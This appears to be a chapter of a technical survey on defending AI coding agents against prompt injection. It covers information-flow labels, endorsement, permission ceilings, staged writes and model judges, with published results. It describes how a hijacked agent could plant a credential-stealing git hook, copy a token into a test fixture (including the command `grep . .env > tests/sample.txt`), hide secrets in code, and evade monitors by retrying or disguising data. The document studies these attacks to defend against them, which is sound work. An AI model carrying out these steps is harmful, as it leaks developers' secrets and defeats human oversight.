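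### Endorsing what the sender couldn't have known

Cecchetti, Myers and Arden (2017) show in *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* that endorsement needs a matching restriction. Their first example is a password checker, which has to endorse a visitor's guess before the guess may influence what the program reveals. If the program labels guesses as secret, faulty or malicious code can pass the stored password to the checker as the guess, and a visitor who doesn't know the password gets in. The secrecy rules allow this because the password only moves from one secret variable to another.

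The remedy is transparent endorsement, which lets a system endorse data only if whoever supplied it could have read it. For the password checker, this means labeling guesses as readable by the visitor. This less secret label makes the program safer because the password can no longer flow into a guess.

In the bug-report example, the test fixture breaks this rule. The agent presents it as the reporter's sample input, but it contains a token that the reporter could not have read. If the maintainer endorsed the fixture, it would count as trusted and meet the main condition for declassification. An attacker could remove both labels this way, one after the other.

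Nonmalleable information flow combines the two restrictions, so the system can remove neither label from data that is both untrusted and secret. It can't declassify the data because an untrusted party influenced it, and it can't endorse the data because that party couldn't have read it. With a cautious context label, a patch that the agent wrote after opening `.env` is both untrusted and secret. The maintainer can still overrule the labels, but safety then depends on what the maintainer notices. The alternative is to produce the patch again from less restricted inputs.

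### An agent that endorses its own work

A hijacked agent could also try to remove labels itself, for example by writing a script that marks the pre-commit hook as trusted. LLMbda, the language for agents designed by Garby and colleagues, has a rule that makes this useless. The label on an endorsed value is

label(control) ⊔ (requested integrity, secrecy of the value),

where label(control) covers everything that influenced the decision to run the endorsement. Suppose a program asks to make an (untrusted, secret) value trusted. If only trusted data led to the request, the result is

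(trusted, public) ⊔ (trusted, secret) = (trusted, secret).

If the program reached the same line because of something in the issue, the result is

(untrusted, public) ⊔ (trusted, secret) = (untrusted, secret),

so the endorsement has cleared nothing. In both cases the value stays secret. Garby and colleagues prove that no endorsement, and no choice of untrusted input, can weaken LLMbda's protection of secrets.

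The rule has a weakness when endorsements follow one another. If the maintainer endorses the text of the issue and the agent then builds a script from it, the script runs in a trusted context and any endorsements inside it take effect. Garby and colleagues prevent this by permanently marking every value that a program endorses and refusing to endorse a marked value again. They also keep the ordinary endorsement command out of model-generated code. They haven't yet found a formal definition of what this achieves.

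LLMbda would let a trusted program endorse the fixture, which transparent endorsement forbids. A coding agent's monitor would need both rules.

### Ways of clearing an agent's files

These rules determine whether a downgrade is open to manipulation, but not whether a particular patch deserves one. Several methods could supply that judgment:

| Method | Who can trigger it | How much can pass | Can it clear distrust? | Can it clear secrecy? |
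|---|---|---|---|---|
| Answer from a fixed list | A trusted context, under the operator's rule | log₂ n bits per answer, for n permitted answers | Yes, for that answer | Only if the operator accepts the leak |
| Separate model as judge | Anyone who can make the agent write something | The whole output, if the judge errs | No | Yes, but not safely if the agent may be hijacked |
| Human approval | The agent asks and a person decides | Everything in the approved item | Yes | Yes, for a named recipient |
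| Tests and scanners | The agent or a build server | The whole file | Only for the property they check | No |
| Code review | Anyone can propose a change and a maintainer decides | The whole change | Yes | Only if the reviewer would recognize the secret |
| Rewriting in a clean context | The maintainer | Whatever the maintainer tells the new session | The new file doesn't need it | The new file doesn't need it |

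### Answers from a fixed list

When FIDES reduces an untrusted document to a yes or no, it records the form of the answer in the label. Yes-or-no answers rank lowest, choices from a list rank higher and free text ranks highest, so a policy can treat them differently.

Garby and colleagues object that this makes exceptions hard to audit. When a value gets through, nobody can tell from that run whether it was the intended exception or a leak that looks the same. They also note that FIDES's own evaluation left the option switched off. In LLMbda, the program has to endorse the value explicitly, and a small wrapper can limit this to a fixed list:

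1. Endorse a copy of the value.
2. Compare the copy with the list.
3. If it matches, return the trusted copy. Otherwise, return the original, which is still untrusted.

Checking a value first and then endorsing it does not work, although that order is more natural. The check would read an untrusted value, so the endorsement would depend on an untrusted decision and would not remove the label.

This method suits decisions about what to do next, such as which component a bug belongs to. It can't clear a patch, because nobody can list all the acceptable patches in advance. Garby and colleagues ran into the same limit with bank tasks, where their agent, Randori, had to take account numbers and amounts from untrusted files. Randori endorses such values anyway. Using Qwen3.7-plus, it completed 36 of 48 runs with these endorsements and 30 without them. Using MiMo-v2.5, it completed 31 with them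 and 26 without. These differences are small compared with the uncertainty in the results.

They justify these endorsements by what the user delegated. A user who asks an agent to pay the bill in a file has authorized it to trust the account number in that file. The delegation is less clear when a user asks an agent to fix a bug that a stranger reported. The user has presumably authorized the agent to rely on the stranger's description of the crash, but has not authorized it to add a hook or change AGENTS.md.

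### A separate model as judge

A second model could read a file and decide whether it is safe to release. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes FlowSeal, which does this for personal assistants with access to private email and documents. Ordinary code intercepts every attempt to write or share something. If the recipient is unknown and the agent may have read protected records, the code sends those records and the proposed output to a separate model. That model must answer SAFE or BLOCKED, and is instructed to block anything that reveals, confirms, denies or paraphrases a record.

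Shim and colleagues tested FlowSeal against attackers who manipulate an honest assistant. In one attack, the attacker creates a shared page with true and false statements about somebody's health and asks the assistant to delete the false ones. The assistant writes nothing secret, but the attacker learns that the remaining statements are true. This attack extracted 75.6% of the sensitive items from an assistant defended only by strict written rules, and 2.3% from one using FlowSeal. Across all the attacks, FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% of items. It completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best prompt-based defense.

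The researchers also replaced the judge with a fixed answer, using an attack that presents the request for information as work on a shared document:

| Judge | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Separate model | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always answers BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always answers SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

The judge therefore makes the system usable, and its mistakes determine how much leaks. Shim and colleagues prove that protected data can't reach an unauthorized recipient unless the judge wrongly answers SAFE. They report that the judge sometimes misses paraphrased facts, and that an attacker might split one fact across several messages that each look harmless.

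These results don't apply to a hijacked coding agent, because Shim and colleagues assume that the agent is trustworthy and exclude prompt injection. Once an injection controls the agent, the attacker writes the proposed output that the judge has to read. The attacker could add a comment to the patch claiming that the protected records are only sample data, or hide a token in variable names, where the judge could miss it.

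A hijacked agent can also keep trying. When FlowSeal blocks a message, the agent may reword it and submit it again. If a judge wrongly passed 2% of attempts, and its mistakes were independent, 50 attempts would succeed at least once with probability

1 − 0.98⁵⁰ ≈ 64%.

A judge is useful as an extra filter on files that the labels already allow out, but it shouldn't be allowed to remove a secrecy label from anything a possibly hijacked agent wrote.

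### Human approval

People can make judgments that no fixed rule captures, but they get tired of being asked. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) measures how much labels can reduce the number of requests. It introduces Prudentia, a version of FIDES that shows the model the security policies and the labels on its data. Before opening hidden text, the model has to explain why it needs the text and which tools it will call afterwards.

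Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data once, instead of approving each later action. If an email contains a list of ten things to do, one endorsement can replace ten approvals. Kolluri and colleagues compared four designs on AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini model, counting the requests in successfully completed tasks:

| Design | Requests to the user | Tasks completed without any request |
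|---|---|---|
| User approves every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Labels, with requests only when a check fails | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 requests and FIDES 36.8, although Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% compared with 75.7%).

Kolluri and colleagues assume that users refuse every action that comes from an injection. Evidence on real users casts some doubt on this. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts, above the company's earlier figure of 93%. Most of those prompts probably concern harmless commands, so a high approval rate alone doesn't prove that users are careless.

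A test by Anthropic gives more direct evidence. According to Hyrax, a software blog, testers caught 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands (13.6%). The share they blocked fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automatic classifier caught 89% of the same commands. Hyrax also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code proposes, which suggests that they read plans more carefully than single commands.

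This favors asking people a few substantial questions, as Prudentia does, but a mistake then does more damage. Wrongly approving one command gives the attacker one action. If the maintainer instead endorses the issue without noticing the injection, the agent's context stays trusted, and the agent can install the hook and edit AGENTS.md without asking again. Endorsing a whole document is reasonable only when somebody can read all of it, including any text the web page normally hides.

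Prudentia doesn't give users a general way to declassify data. Kolluri and colleagues argue that whether to release private information depends heavily on the situation, so users should approve each release separately. A coding agent's request to release a file should therefore name the file and its destination. The monitor should add the file's origin and labels, because a hijacked agent could describe the file misleadingly.

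Human approval can justify removing the label from a setting that the maintainer recognizes, but it's a poor reason to remove the label from a long patch written by an agent that has read the token.

### Tests, scanners and reviews

Software projects already have ways of deciding whether to accept code. Each of them establishes something specific, and none of them establishes that a file is harmless in general:

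| Check | What a pass establishes | What stays open |
|---|---|---|
| Test for the reported crash | The program no longer crashes on that input | Whether the patch also does something else |
| Full test suite | The program gave the expected results on the tested inputs, in the test environment | Other inputs, and code that behaves differently outside the test environment |
| Secret scanner | The file contains no text that matches the scanner's patterns | Encoded secrets, and secrets with no recognizable format |
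| Vulnerability scanner | The scanner's rules found no match in the code it could analyze | Flaws that the rules don't describe |
| Dependency scanner | No listed package version has a known problem | Malicious packages that nobody has reported |
| Formal proof | The program meets a stated specification | Anything that the specification leaves out |
| Digital signature | The holder of a key signed exactly these contents | Whether the signer checked them |
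| Code review | A particular person read this version and accepted it | Whatever that person overlooked or didn't open |

A hijacked agent that can run automatic checks as often as it likes can keep revising a harmful patch until every check passes. It can also weaken the checks by editing the tests, which are ordinary files in the project. The build server should therefore run the tests from the main branch, with their original configuration, and treat any tests that the agent changed as part of the patch.

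A passing check should add a record and leave the label in place. The record might list the file's hash and the version of the test suite it passed. A policy can then require several such records before anyone can merge the file. This avoids treating a narrow result, such as the absence of known vulnerabilities, as a reason to trust the file for every purpose.

None of the automatic checks can clear a secrecy label. A secret scanner can miss a secret that has been encoded. A formal proof could in principle show that a program doesn't reveal a secret while it runs, but the secret could still be in the program's source code.

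Code review comes closest to an endorsement in the strict sense, because a person with authority over the project accepts the change. But the review covers only what the reviewer sees. Git leaves hooks out of commits, so a maintainer can read every line of a pull request without seeing the pre-commit hook on the developer's machine.

### Rewriting the change in a clean context

If the agent's patch is too risky to clear, somebody can discard it and have a new session write another one using only trusted inputs. The ordinary rule for joins then gives the new patch a trusted label, so nobody has to grant an exception.

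Randori similarly writes a complete program for the user's task before it reads any untrusted data. First attempts often contain errors, so the agent tests the program on made-up data, where reading a file always returns the same placeholder text. The error messages that guide its revisions therefore contain no untrusted data. The program runs on the real data only once it is finished, so the model chooses any endorsements in the program before an attacker can influence it.

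This is harder for a bug fix, because the task depends on the stranger's report. The maintainer can read the issue and describe the crash to the new session in their own words, such as "the parser fails when a header is empty." The stranger still influences which problem the maintainer describes, but the injected instructions don't reach the model. The maintainer's sentence is an endorsement, and a fairly safe one because the maintainer wrote and understood all of it.

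The new session must not see the first patch, a summary by the first agent, or the token. Even using the old patch to choose among new ones leaks some information from it. If the developer generates eight clean patches and picks the one most like the original, the choice can carry up to three bits of that information.

The method requires a second run, and it doesn't work for every bug. If the crash occurs only with a complicated input file that the reporter attached, a short description may not be enough to find the cause. A trusted label also doesn't make the code correct. The model may introduce a vulnerability by accident, so the patch still needs tests and a review, but the reviewer no longer has to assume that an attacker designed it.

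### A policy for the four artifacts

For the bug-report example, these methods can be combined into a policy with one kind of approval. Each approval answers all four of Sabelfeld and Sands's questions:

```
what:    the file with this exact hash
who:     a maintainer, outside the agent's session
where:   merging into the main branch
when:    after the main branch's own tests pass
removes: untrusted
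```

An approval for merging doesn't allow anything else, such as running the file with access to `.env`. Any edit changes the hash and cancels the approval. The monitor ignores attempts by the agent's session to remove a label, because that session has read the issue. The four artifacts then go through as follows:

| Artifact | Label | What the policy does |
|---|---|---|
| Source patch, finished before the agent opened `.env` | untrusted, public | Runs the tests in a sandbox without secrets or a network, then asks a maintainer to review and approve the patch |
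| Source patch, finished afterwards | untrusted, secret | Refuses to clear it; a clean session writes a new patch |
| Test fixture | untrusted, secret | Refuses to clear it; a session that never reads `.env` builds a new fixture with invented settings, and a maintainer reviews it |
| Pre-commit hook | untrusted, public | Deletes it, because the developer didn't ask for a hook |
| Line in AGENTS.md | untrusted, public | Restores the previous version; only a maintainer may change the file, outside an agent session |

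The patch can still contain a backdoor that both the tests and the reviewer miss. The new fixture may also depend on the stranger's sample input, so it keeps its untrusted label until the review.

If the agent opened `.env` after reading the issue, the maintainer should also revoke the token and create a new one, because the agent may have leaked it through a channel that the monitor doesn't cover. Revoking the token also gives the maintainer another way to rescue the later patch, because the old token no longer works and can be declassified. This declassification is robust because no stranger influenced the token or the decision to revoke it. If `.env` held no other secrets, the monitor can recompute the patch's label as (untrusted, public) and send the patch to review.

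## What do permissions and held writes add to labels?

The policy for the four artifacts deletes the pre-commit hook after the agent has written it. A harness could instead refuse the write, because fixing a crash doesn't require a hook. It could also keep the hook in a temporary copy of the project, where the developer's own Git never runs it. Both approaches limit what a hijacked agent can do without having to work out which inputs influenced the model.

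### Permissions that come before the untrusted text

Many coding agents can act on any file or command they can name, within whatever sandbox they run in. Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, present CapScope, which gives each agent a list of permissions instead. A permission combines a kind of operation (reading, writing or executing) with a limit on its scope, such as files under `src/`. CapScope keeps the list outside the model's context and applies three rules:

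1. Mint creates the permissions. Before the agent reads any file, a separate model call receives only the developer's request and the names of the project's files, and predicts what the task will need. Ordinary code checks the prediction and fixes it as a ceiling for the whole task.
2. Derive narrows them. When the main agent delegates work, the sub-agent receives only those requested permissions that fit under the ceiling.
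3. Invoke checks them. A tool call runs only if the agent that made it holds a permission that covers it.

If φ and φ′ are the limits of two permissions for the same kind of operation, the second fits within the first when

φ′(a) ⇒ φ(a) for every argument a.

An injection can change what an agent asks for, but it can't raise the ceiling.

Bouras and colleagues use the example of a developer who wants to fix failing login tests to explain why permissions need narrowing. A poisoned test prints a fake notice that a signing key has changed and gives a new value to put in `src/auth/keys.py`. An attacker who knows that key can forge login tokens. The repair requires write access to `src/`, so a single policy for the whole task has to allow the harmful edit. CapScope runs the tests in a sub-agent that can't write files and leaves source edits to another sub-agent, which doesn't run the tests.

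The researchers tested this on five small Python projects with one bug each. They put an injection in one of five places: the README, AGENTS.md, a skill file, a source comment or the test output. The injection asked for something ordinary but unnecessary, such as running one of the project's own utilities. With four sets of permissions and three trials of each combination, this made 300 runs:

| Permissions | Injected action took effect | Repairs completed | Mean time |
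|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| A fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy per task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The model attempted the injected action in 34 of the CapScope runs, so the low number comes mainly from the checks rather than the model's caution. Many agents kept trying after being refused, which accounts for some of the extra time.

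Only two of CapScope's seven failed repairs happened because the ceiling was too low. In two others, the sub-agent running the tests proposed the right edit, but the main agent didn't pass it to the sub-agent that could make it. The other three passed their tests but reached the time limit.

All three successful attacks came through AGENTS.md, which the main agent usually reads. Injected text can influence how the main agent describes a subtask, and therefore which permissions the sub-agent gets. Bouras and colleagues note that an attack can still succeed this way if the ceiling allows the action.

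The test was small, with five one-bug projects and one model (qwen3.5-flash). Predicting permissions is probably harder in the bug-report example, because a request to fix a numbered issue doesn't reveal which files matter, and the model that makes the prediction can't read the issue. The ceiling would have to cover most of the source code, or the developer would have to approve additions during the task. CapScope supports such approvals, but the test ran without them.

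### A permitted read and a permitted write

If the ceiling for the bug fix covers the source files, the tests and the test command, CapScope blocks a direct write to the hook or to AGENTS.md. The agent can still copy the token into the test fixture, because the tested version lets agents read the whole repository and the fixture is among the tests. Bouras and colleagues state that CapScope does not protect confidentiality, since a permitted read followed by a permitted write can move data.

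Narrower read permissions wouldn't solve this on their own. CapScope always admits commands such as `grep` and `find`, even for files outside an agent's read permissions, and it ignores redirections when it checks a command. By those rules, this command would pass as a read, although it copies the token into a file:

```
grep . .env > tests/sample.txt
```

Test runners create another gap. An agent that may edit tests and run `pytest` can write a test that installs the hook. CapScope detects only the permitted command, so it relies on a separate sandbox to restrict what that command does.

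Other designs change what the permissions can express or what enforces them. *AGENTCAP* (2026) forbids certain combinations of permissions and also checks where arguments came from, while *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (2026) uses an operating system kernel to control which functions an agent may call.

### Holding effects until there is more evidence

CapScope has to accept or refuse a call immediately, but KAIROS, a virtual-machine monitor that Hempel and colleagues built, can postpone the decision. The virtual machine has three connections to the outside: the project's files, the network and the developer's terminal. A tool call and a script that the agent wrote look the same at these connections, so the agent can't avoid the monitor by using a script.

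Hempel and colleagues distinguish confinement from authorization. Confinement means that the monitor controls everything that leaves the machine, and it consists of three guarantees:

- Every effect passes through the monitor.
- No effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it.
- An effect that the monitor refuses never becomes visible outside.

These guarantees hold even if the agent is fully hostile, as long as the virtual machine has no other exits and the monitor, the host and the model provider are trustworthy. They don't cover covert channels. Authorization, the choice of which effects to release, has no such guarantee because it depends on a policy and on somebody's judgment.

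The monitor holds different effects in different ways:

| Effect | How KAIROS holds it | What the agent receives meanwhile |
|---|---|---|
| Writing or deleting a project file | Applies it to a layer above the real files | Its own changed version of the project |
| A request that changes something on a server | Stops it at a proxy | A placeholder response |
| A request that fetches data | Cannot hold it, so decides first | Nothing until the decision |

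The policy first checks whether a rule forbids an effect, and refuses it if so. Otherwise, it checks whether the values that control the effect, such as a command or a destination, came from a trusted source, and whether the data may go to that destination. It releases effects that pass both checks and sends the rest to a judge. The judge can be a person, but by default it is a separate model that is given the developer's task, the agent's earlier actions and the origin of each value. The judge can't overrule a refusal.

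### The hook in a staged copy

With the malicious setup guide described earlier, KAIROS handles the pre-commit hook like this:

1. The agent writes the hook. Its commands come from an untrusted guide, so the policy defers the write, and the hook exists only in the staged layer.
2. The agent makes a commit. Git runs inside the virtual machine, finds the staged hook and starts it.
3. The hook tries to send the developer's private key to the attacker, and the policy refuses the request.
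4. The judge sees the attempt and rejects the hook. KAIROS discards it, so the real project never contains it, and tells the agent.

A monitor that could only allow or refuse would have had to decide at the first step, when the hook looked like many legitimate ones. KAIROS can't undo the agent's memory, though. The agent needs the notice because it may still remember a placeholder response for something that never happened.

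The extra evidence appears only if the hook runs before the monitor has to decide. KAIROS settles everything it holds by the end of the task. In the bug-report example, the hook runs at the developer's next commit, which may come after that, and the judge would then have to decide before the hook had done anything. An attacker could also write a hook that does nothing inside a virtual machine. A rule that forbids writes to the hooks directory would be safer here because it doesn't depend on how the hook behaves.

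### Labels at the boundary

KAIROS doesn't track data inside the agent, but it keeps labels. Every location the agent writes to inherits the combined labels of everything the agent read beforehand, so a patch gets roughly the label that a cautious context label would give it. Without this rule, an agent could copy a stranger's instructions into a notes file and later read them back as trusted project text. The label is provisional while the file is in the staged layer and becomes permanent when the monitor releases the file.

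KAIROS authorizes outgoing requests using the value matching described earlier, which depends on the agent not disguising values. If the agent disguises a trusted address, the monitor no longer recognizes it and defers the request, but the monitor may release a disguised token because it no longer matches the secret.

Ordinary tools can cause similar failures. Hempel and colleagues note that data from a secret file is no longer treated as sensitive if the agent moves it elsewhere before reading it. Git compresses the files it pushes, so a search of the outgoing request would probably miss the token in the fixture. The monitor would have to unpack the push or look up the label on each file in it.

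### Results with simulated tools

Hempel and colleagues compared KAIROS on AgentDojo with CaMeL, which plans all its steps in advance, and Progent, which checks tool calls against a policy that a model derives from the task. With GPT-4.1 as the agent, the results were:

| Defense | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47.0% | 82.7% | 59.8% |
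| CaMeL | 0.2% | 38.0% | 40.7% |
| Progent | 11.5% | 78.2% | 57.6% |
| KAIROS | 2.7% | 85.1% | 69.5% |

In a strict mode that refused everything the policy would have deferred, KAIROS completed only 42.7% of tasks when there was no attack, and the attack success rate was about the same as with the judge. On this benchmark, the policy provided the security, and the judge let the agent complete more tasks. In runs without an attack, the policy released 83% of effects by itself, and the judge wrongly refused only one of the others.

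AgentDyn, which has 60 open-ended tasks, is closer to debugging because the agent has to keep planning as it finds things out. On these tasks, KAIROS reduced attack success from 37.8% to 1.7%. Task completion without an attack hardly changed (53.3% to 51.7%), but completion under attack fell from 55.5% to 37.1%. Progent also reduced attack success to 1.7%, but it completed only 6.7% of tasks without an attack. The researchers left out CaMeL because its plan is fixed before the task begins.

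Repeated holds explain much of KAIROS's loss of utility. Tasks that continued past one held effect kept 90% of their utility, but those that continued past two or more kept 62%. Each approval covers a single effect, so the next use of the same untrusted value causes another hold. A long session based on a stranger's bug report could be held often.

In AutoDojo, an automated attacker rewrites its injections over six rounds. Attacks succeeded 8.8% of the time against KAIROS, 7.7% against Progent and 52.4% with no defense. The attacks that got past KAIROS were in tasks where the user delegated authority to a document, and the judge treated the document's instructions as the user's own. A request to fix the bug described in an issue could mislead the judge in the same way.

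All three benchmarks simulate their tools in memory, without a repository, a shell or a virtual machine. An adapter translated each tool call into an event that KAIROS could check. The results therefore test the policy and the judge, not the machine's boundary or real coding work. The agent models (GPT-4.1, GPT-4o and GPT-4o-mini) are also old. In speed measurements, the real boundary added about 2 milliseconds to a file operation and 1 millisecond to a request.

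### Staging and judging in real repositories

*Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) points out that documentation in software repositories often contains legitimate commands. A monitor therefore can't assume that every command in a README is an attack. Two groups tested parts of the KAIROS approach on more realistic coding work.

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) presents YoloFS, a filesystem that stages an agent's changes until the user accepts them. It also records what each command changed, so the agent can inspect and undo its own work. The paper tests YoloFS with Claude Code, Copilot and Gemini. The agents noticed and reversed the damage in 8 of 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects. In the other three, the changes looked to the agent like part of the task, but they remained staged for the user to reject.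 On 112 routine tasks, the agents succeeded 99% of the time, the same as without YoloFS, and needed fewer answers from the user.

This is good evidence that staging works with ordinary coding agents, but mostly as protection against accidents. Zhong and colleagues studied 290 public reports of file misuse, 21 of which involved prompt injection. A hijacked agent has no reason to undo the hook it was told to install, so the user's review matters more. Staging also can't retract a secret that has left the machine, so YoloFS asks the user before sensitive reads.

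*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) tested a judge without staging. A model decides whether a program's requests to the operating system are safe and necessary for the task, while fixed rules and stored decisions handle routine requests. A refused operation fails before it takes effect, and the rest of the program can continue. In a test that added 340 attacks to real bug fixes from the SWE-bench Verified benchmark, AgentBouncer reduced attack success from 99.41% to 10.59%. The agent solved about as many tasks with it (72.94%) as without it (71.47%).

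Their attacks deleted system files, stole data or took control of the machine, often through a script or a tool with a harmless description. A judge that sees the actual operation has a clear advantage here. None of the attacks put a backdoor in the patch itself, where the judge would see only an ordinary write to a source file.

### Checking origin and permission together

Staging changes also lets a monitor examine a whole task at once. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that reads logs containing a password-like key, summarizes them and prepares a Slack message. Each step is reasonable, but together they could publish the key. Cordon holds the file changes and the message, records which results came from which, and checks the complete chain before releasing anything. It stopped all 45 risky workflows in the paper's test, compared with 14 for simplified versions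 of existing defenses.

Chen and colleagues designed those workflows around risks that span several steps, so the comparison favors Cordon. Cordon also works at the level of tool calls and needs a description of what each tool does. Its snapshots leave out `.git` to save time, but Git hooks are normally stored there, so the prototype might miss the hook.

PACE, which Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PACE*, describe, makes both checks immediately before each tool call. The origin check builds a graph of where the call's arguments came from. If secret or untrusted data can reach a dangerous call, PACE looks for the cheapest way to break the connection:

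cost = min(cost of blocking the call, total cost of cutting every affected argument)

PACE nearly always blocks the call, because removing an argument breaks the connection only if the model would have made the call regardless of that argument, and PACE usually can't establish this. The permission check compares the call's effects with what the user's request authorizes, including the resource, the arguments and a time limit. Text generated by the model can't add permissions.

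Li and colleagues prove that a strict version of PACE keeps the two sides separate if its graph includes every relevant connection. They tested a looser version, in which the permission check can restore a call that the origin check would have blocked. This version had the lowest attack success in 62 of 79 comparisons across eight benchmarks and tied for the lowest in another 14. An adaptive attacker succeeded in none of 30 cases, compared with 21 without a defense, but all 30 goals lay outside what the user had authorized.

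The researchers also tested the checks separately, with Qwen-3.8-27B on a sample of cases:

| Checks in use | AgentDojo attacks that succeeded | AgentDojo tasks completed | AgentDyn attacks that succeeded | AgentDyn tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Origin only | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Permissions only | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Both | 0.0% | 65.2% | 1.7% | 36.7% |

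The origin check alone blocked almost all useful work, much as cautious labels did in the FIDES tests. Permissions alone stopped nearly as many attacks and blocked far less useful work. Adding the origin check to permissions made almost no difference, because the permission check could restore whatever the origin check had blocked. The tested version's success is therefore mainly evidence for permissions.

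Tracking is still necessary, because an attack can stay within the user's permissions. PACE recognizes secrets in several common encodings, such as base64, but it misses paraphrases, translations and short fragments. It also can't follow a secret through calls that a tool makes internally, which is a serious gap for an agent whose main tool is a shell.

### What each mechanism stops

The differences are easiest to see in what a hijacked agent might try in the bug-report example. The last column assumes a cautious context label and a monitor that follows files and processes:

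| What the agent tries | Permissions fixed in advance | Held effects | Labels |
|---|---|---|---|
| Write the hook or the line in AGENTS.md directly | Refuse it if the task doesn't include those files | Keep it out of the real project until release | Allow the write but mark the file untrusted |
| Install the hook through a test | Miss it without a sandbox | Keep it out of the real project until release | Allow the write but mark the file untrusted |
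| Copy the token into the fixture | Allow it if the agent may read `.env` and write tests | Leave it to the judge | Stop the file at the push |
| Hide the token in the patch's variable names | Allow it on the same condition | Leave it to a judge who may see nothing wrong | Stop the patch at the push |
| Signal the token by choosing which branch to push | Refuse it if the agent may not push | Delay the push, but probably release it | Stop it only if the policy also checks the decision to push |
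| Put a backdoor in the patch | Allow it | Leave it to the judge | Keep the patch untrusted until review |

Permissions and held writes can stop a harmful file before anything else on the developer's machine reads or runs it. A label can do this only if the editor, Git or the next agent session checks it. Permissions also keep working when a label is wrong. If someone has mistakenly marked the issue tracker as trusted, a limit on permissions based on the developer's request still stops the agent from writing the hook.

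Labels, in turn, stop secrets, including disguised ones, that travel through permitted operations. They also remain useful after the monitor releases a file. CapScope's permissions expire with the session, and a staged patch becomes an ordinary file once somebody accepts it. If the patch keeps its untrusted label, a build server or another agent can still treat it differently from code that a maintainer has reviewed.

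Permissions can also reduce label creep. If a sandbox prevents the agent and every command it runs from reading `.env`, the agent's context never becomes secret. Its patch is then untrusted but public, so the maintainer can review and publish it without declassifying anything.

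## Which labeling schemes can teams use today?

A label can protect a released file only if one program writes it and another checks it later. Most of the systems that do both, such as FLOWSH and Tether, are research prototypes. But during 2026 Microsoft and GitHub began adding labels to products that developers already use, and software projects have older ways of marking finished files. Five questions help in judging any of these schemes:

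- Who assigns the label?
- Can the agent forge or remove it?
- Does it survive copying and editing?
- What checks it, and does the check come before the harm?
- How much work does it take?

### A labeled tool call

MCP clients and servers exchange messages that have a field called `_meta` for extra information. Microsoft puts labels in this field, so a labeled server still works with clients that don't support labels. In one of its examples, an agent wants to post the announcement date of a new model to a Teams channel. Slightly simplified, the call looks like this:

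```
tool:      SendMessageToChannel
content:   (the announcement)
labels:
  whole call:  untrusted, public
  content:     trusted, readable by two named users
```

The client attaches the labels, so the model can't change them by writing something different. The label on the whole call shows that untrusted text has entered the conversation. The announcement can have a label of its own if the client has kept it in a variable, as FIDES does. Before the tool runs, a policy goes through three steps:

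1. It allows the call if the label on the whole call is trusted, which isn't the case here.
2. It fetches the channel's current members from Teams and computes

   missing = channel members − permitted readers.

   If nobody is missing, it allows the call.
3. Otherwise, it asks the user and lists the people who would gain access.

If the channel has a third member, the user gets a question about that person. As written, the refusal at the end of the policy could apply only if the policy failed to identify who was missing, for instance because Teams didn't return the member list.

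### Prototypes for MCP and Copilot

Users of GitHub's MCP server can turn on labels by adding the header `X-MCP-Features: ifc_labels` to its configuration. The server then labels each result as a whole. According to its documentation, the server's label package, *ifc* (2026), only defines the labels, and a separate service enforces them. The option therefore provides no protection if the client ignores labels.

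Copilot CLI, GitHub's command-line coding agent, has an experimental labeling mode. When a developer starts it with `FIDES_IFC=true`, the program keeps a context label, updates it after every tool result and attaches it to every tool call. The mode enforces policies only for selected tools from GitHub's MCP server and doesn't yet support other servers.

In the bug-report example, this mode would mark the context as untrusted once the agent fetched the issue through the server. It could then stop the agent from copying a private repository's contents into a public comment. But the agent would probably open `.env` with a local tool and push the fixture with a `git` command, and Microsoft doesn't describe a policy for either action.

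Teams that build their own agents can use a more complete scheme in the Microsoft Agent Framework, a library for writing agents. Its security module runs code before and after each tool call. It can hide untrusted results in variables, send questions about them to a quarantined model, and either block a forbidden call or ask the user whether to allow it. A developer turns this on with a few settings and lists the tools that may run in an untrusted context. In Microsoft's example, the list for an agent that sorts GitHub issues includes the tool for reading issues but not the tools for posting comments and writing files.

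For other MCP servers, Microsoft offers an open-source gateway that adds labels to messages as they pass through. Setting it up is reasonable for five tools but a lot of work for fifty, because someone has to describe each tool's output format, write a Python function that computes the label for its results, and write or choose a policy.

None of these prototypes solves the problem of finished files, because the labels are attached to messages and not to what the agent saves.

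### Hints and a proposed standard

A method that takes less work uses hints that many MCP servers already publish about their tools, such as whether a tool only reads data and whether it contacts the outside world. Microsoft suggests always allowing tools that only read from a closed system, allowing tools that read from the outside world only if their arguments are public, and asking the user about destructive tools. A client could also label every result from the outside world as untrusted and every result that requires a login as private.

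The Model Context Protocol (2026) blog warns that a server's hints can describe a tool as read-only even if it deletes files, so clients must not trust hints from untrusted servers. Many servers publish no hints. By default, the protocol then classifies the tool as destructive and open to the outside world, but clients differ in how strictly they follow this rule.

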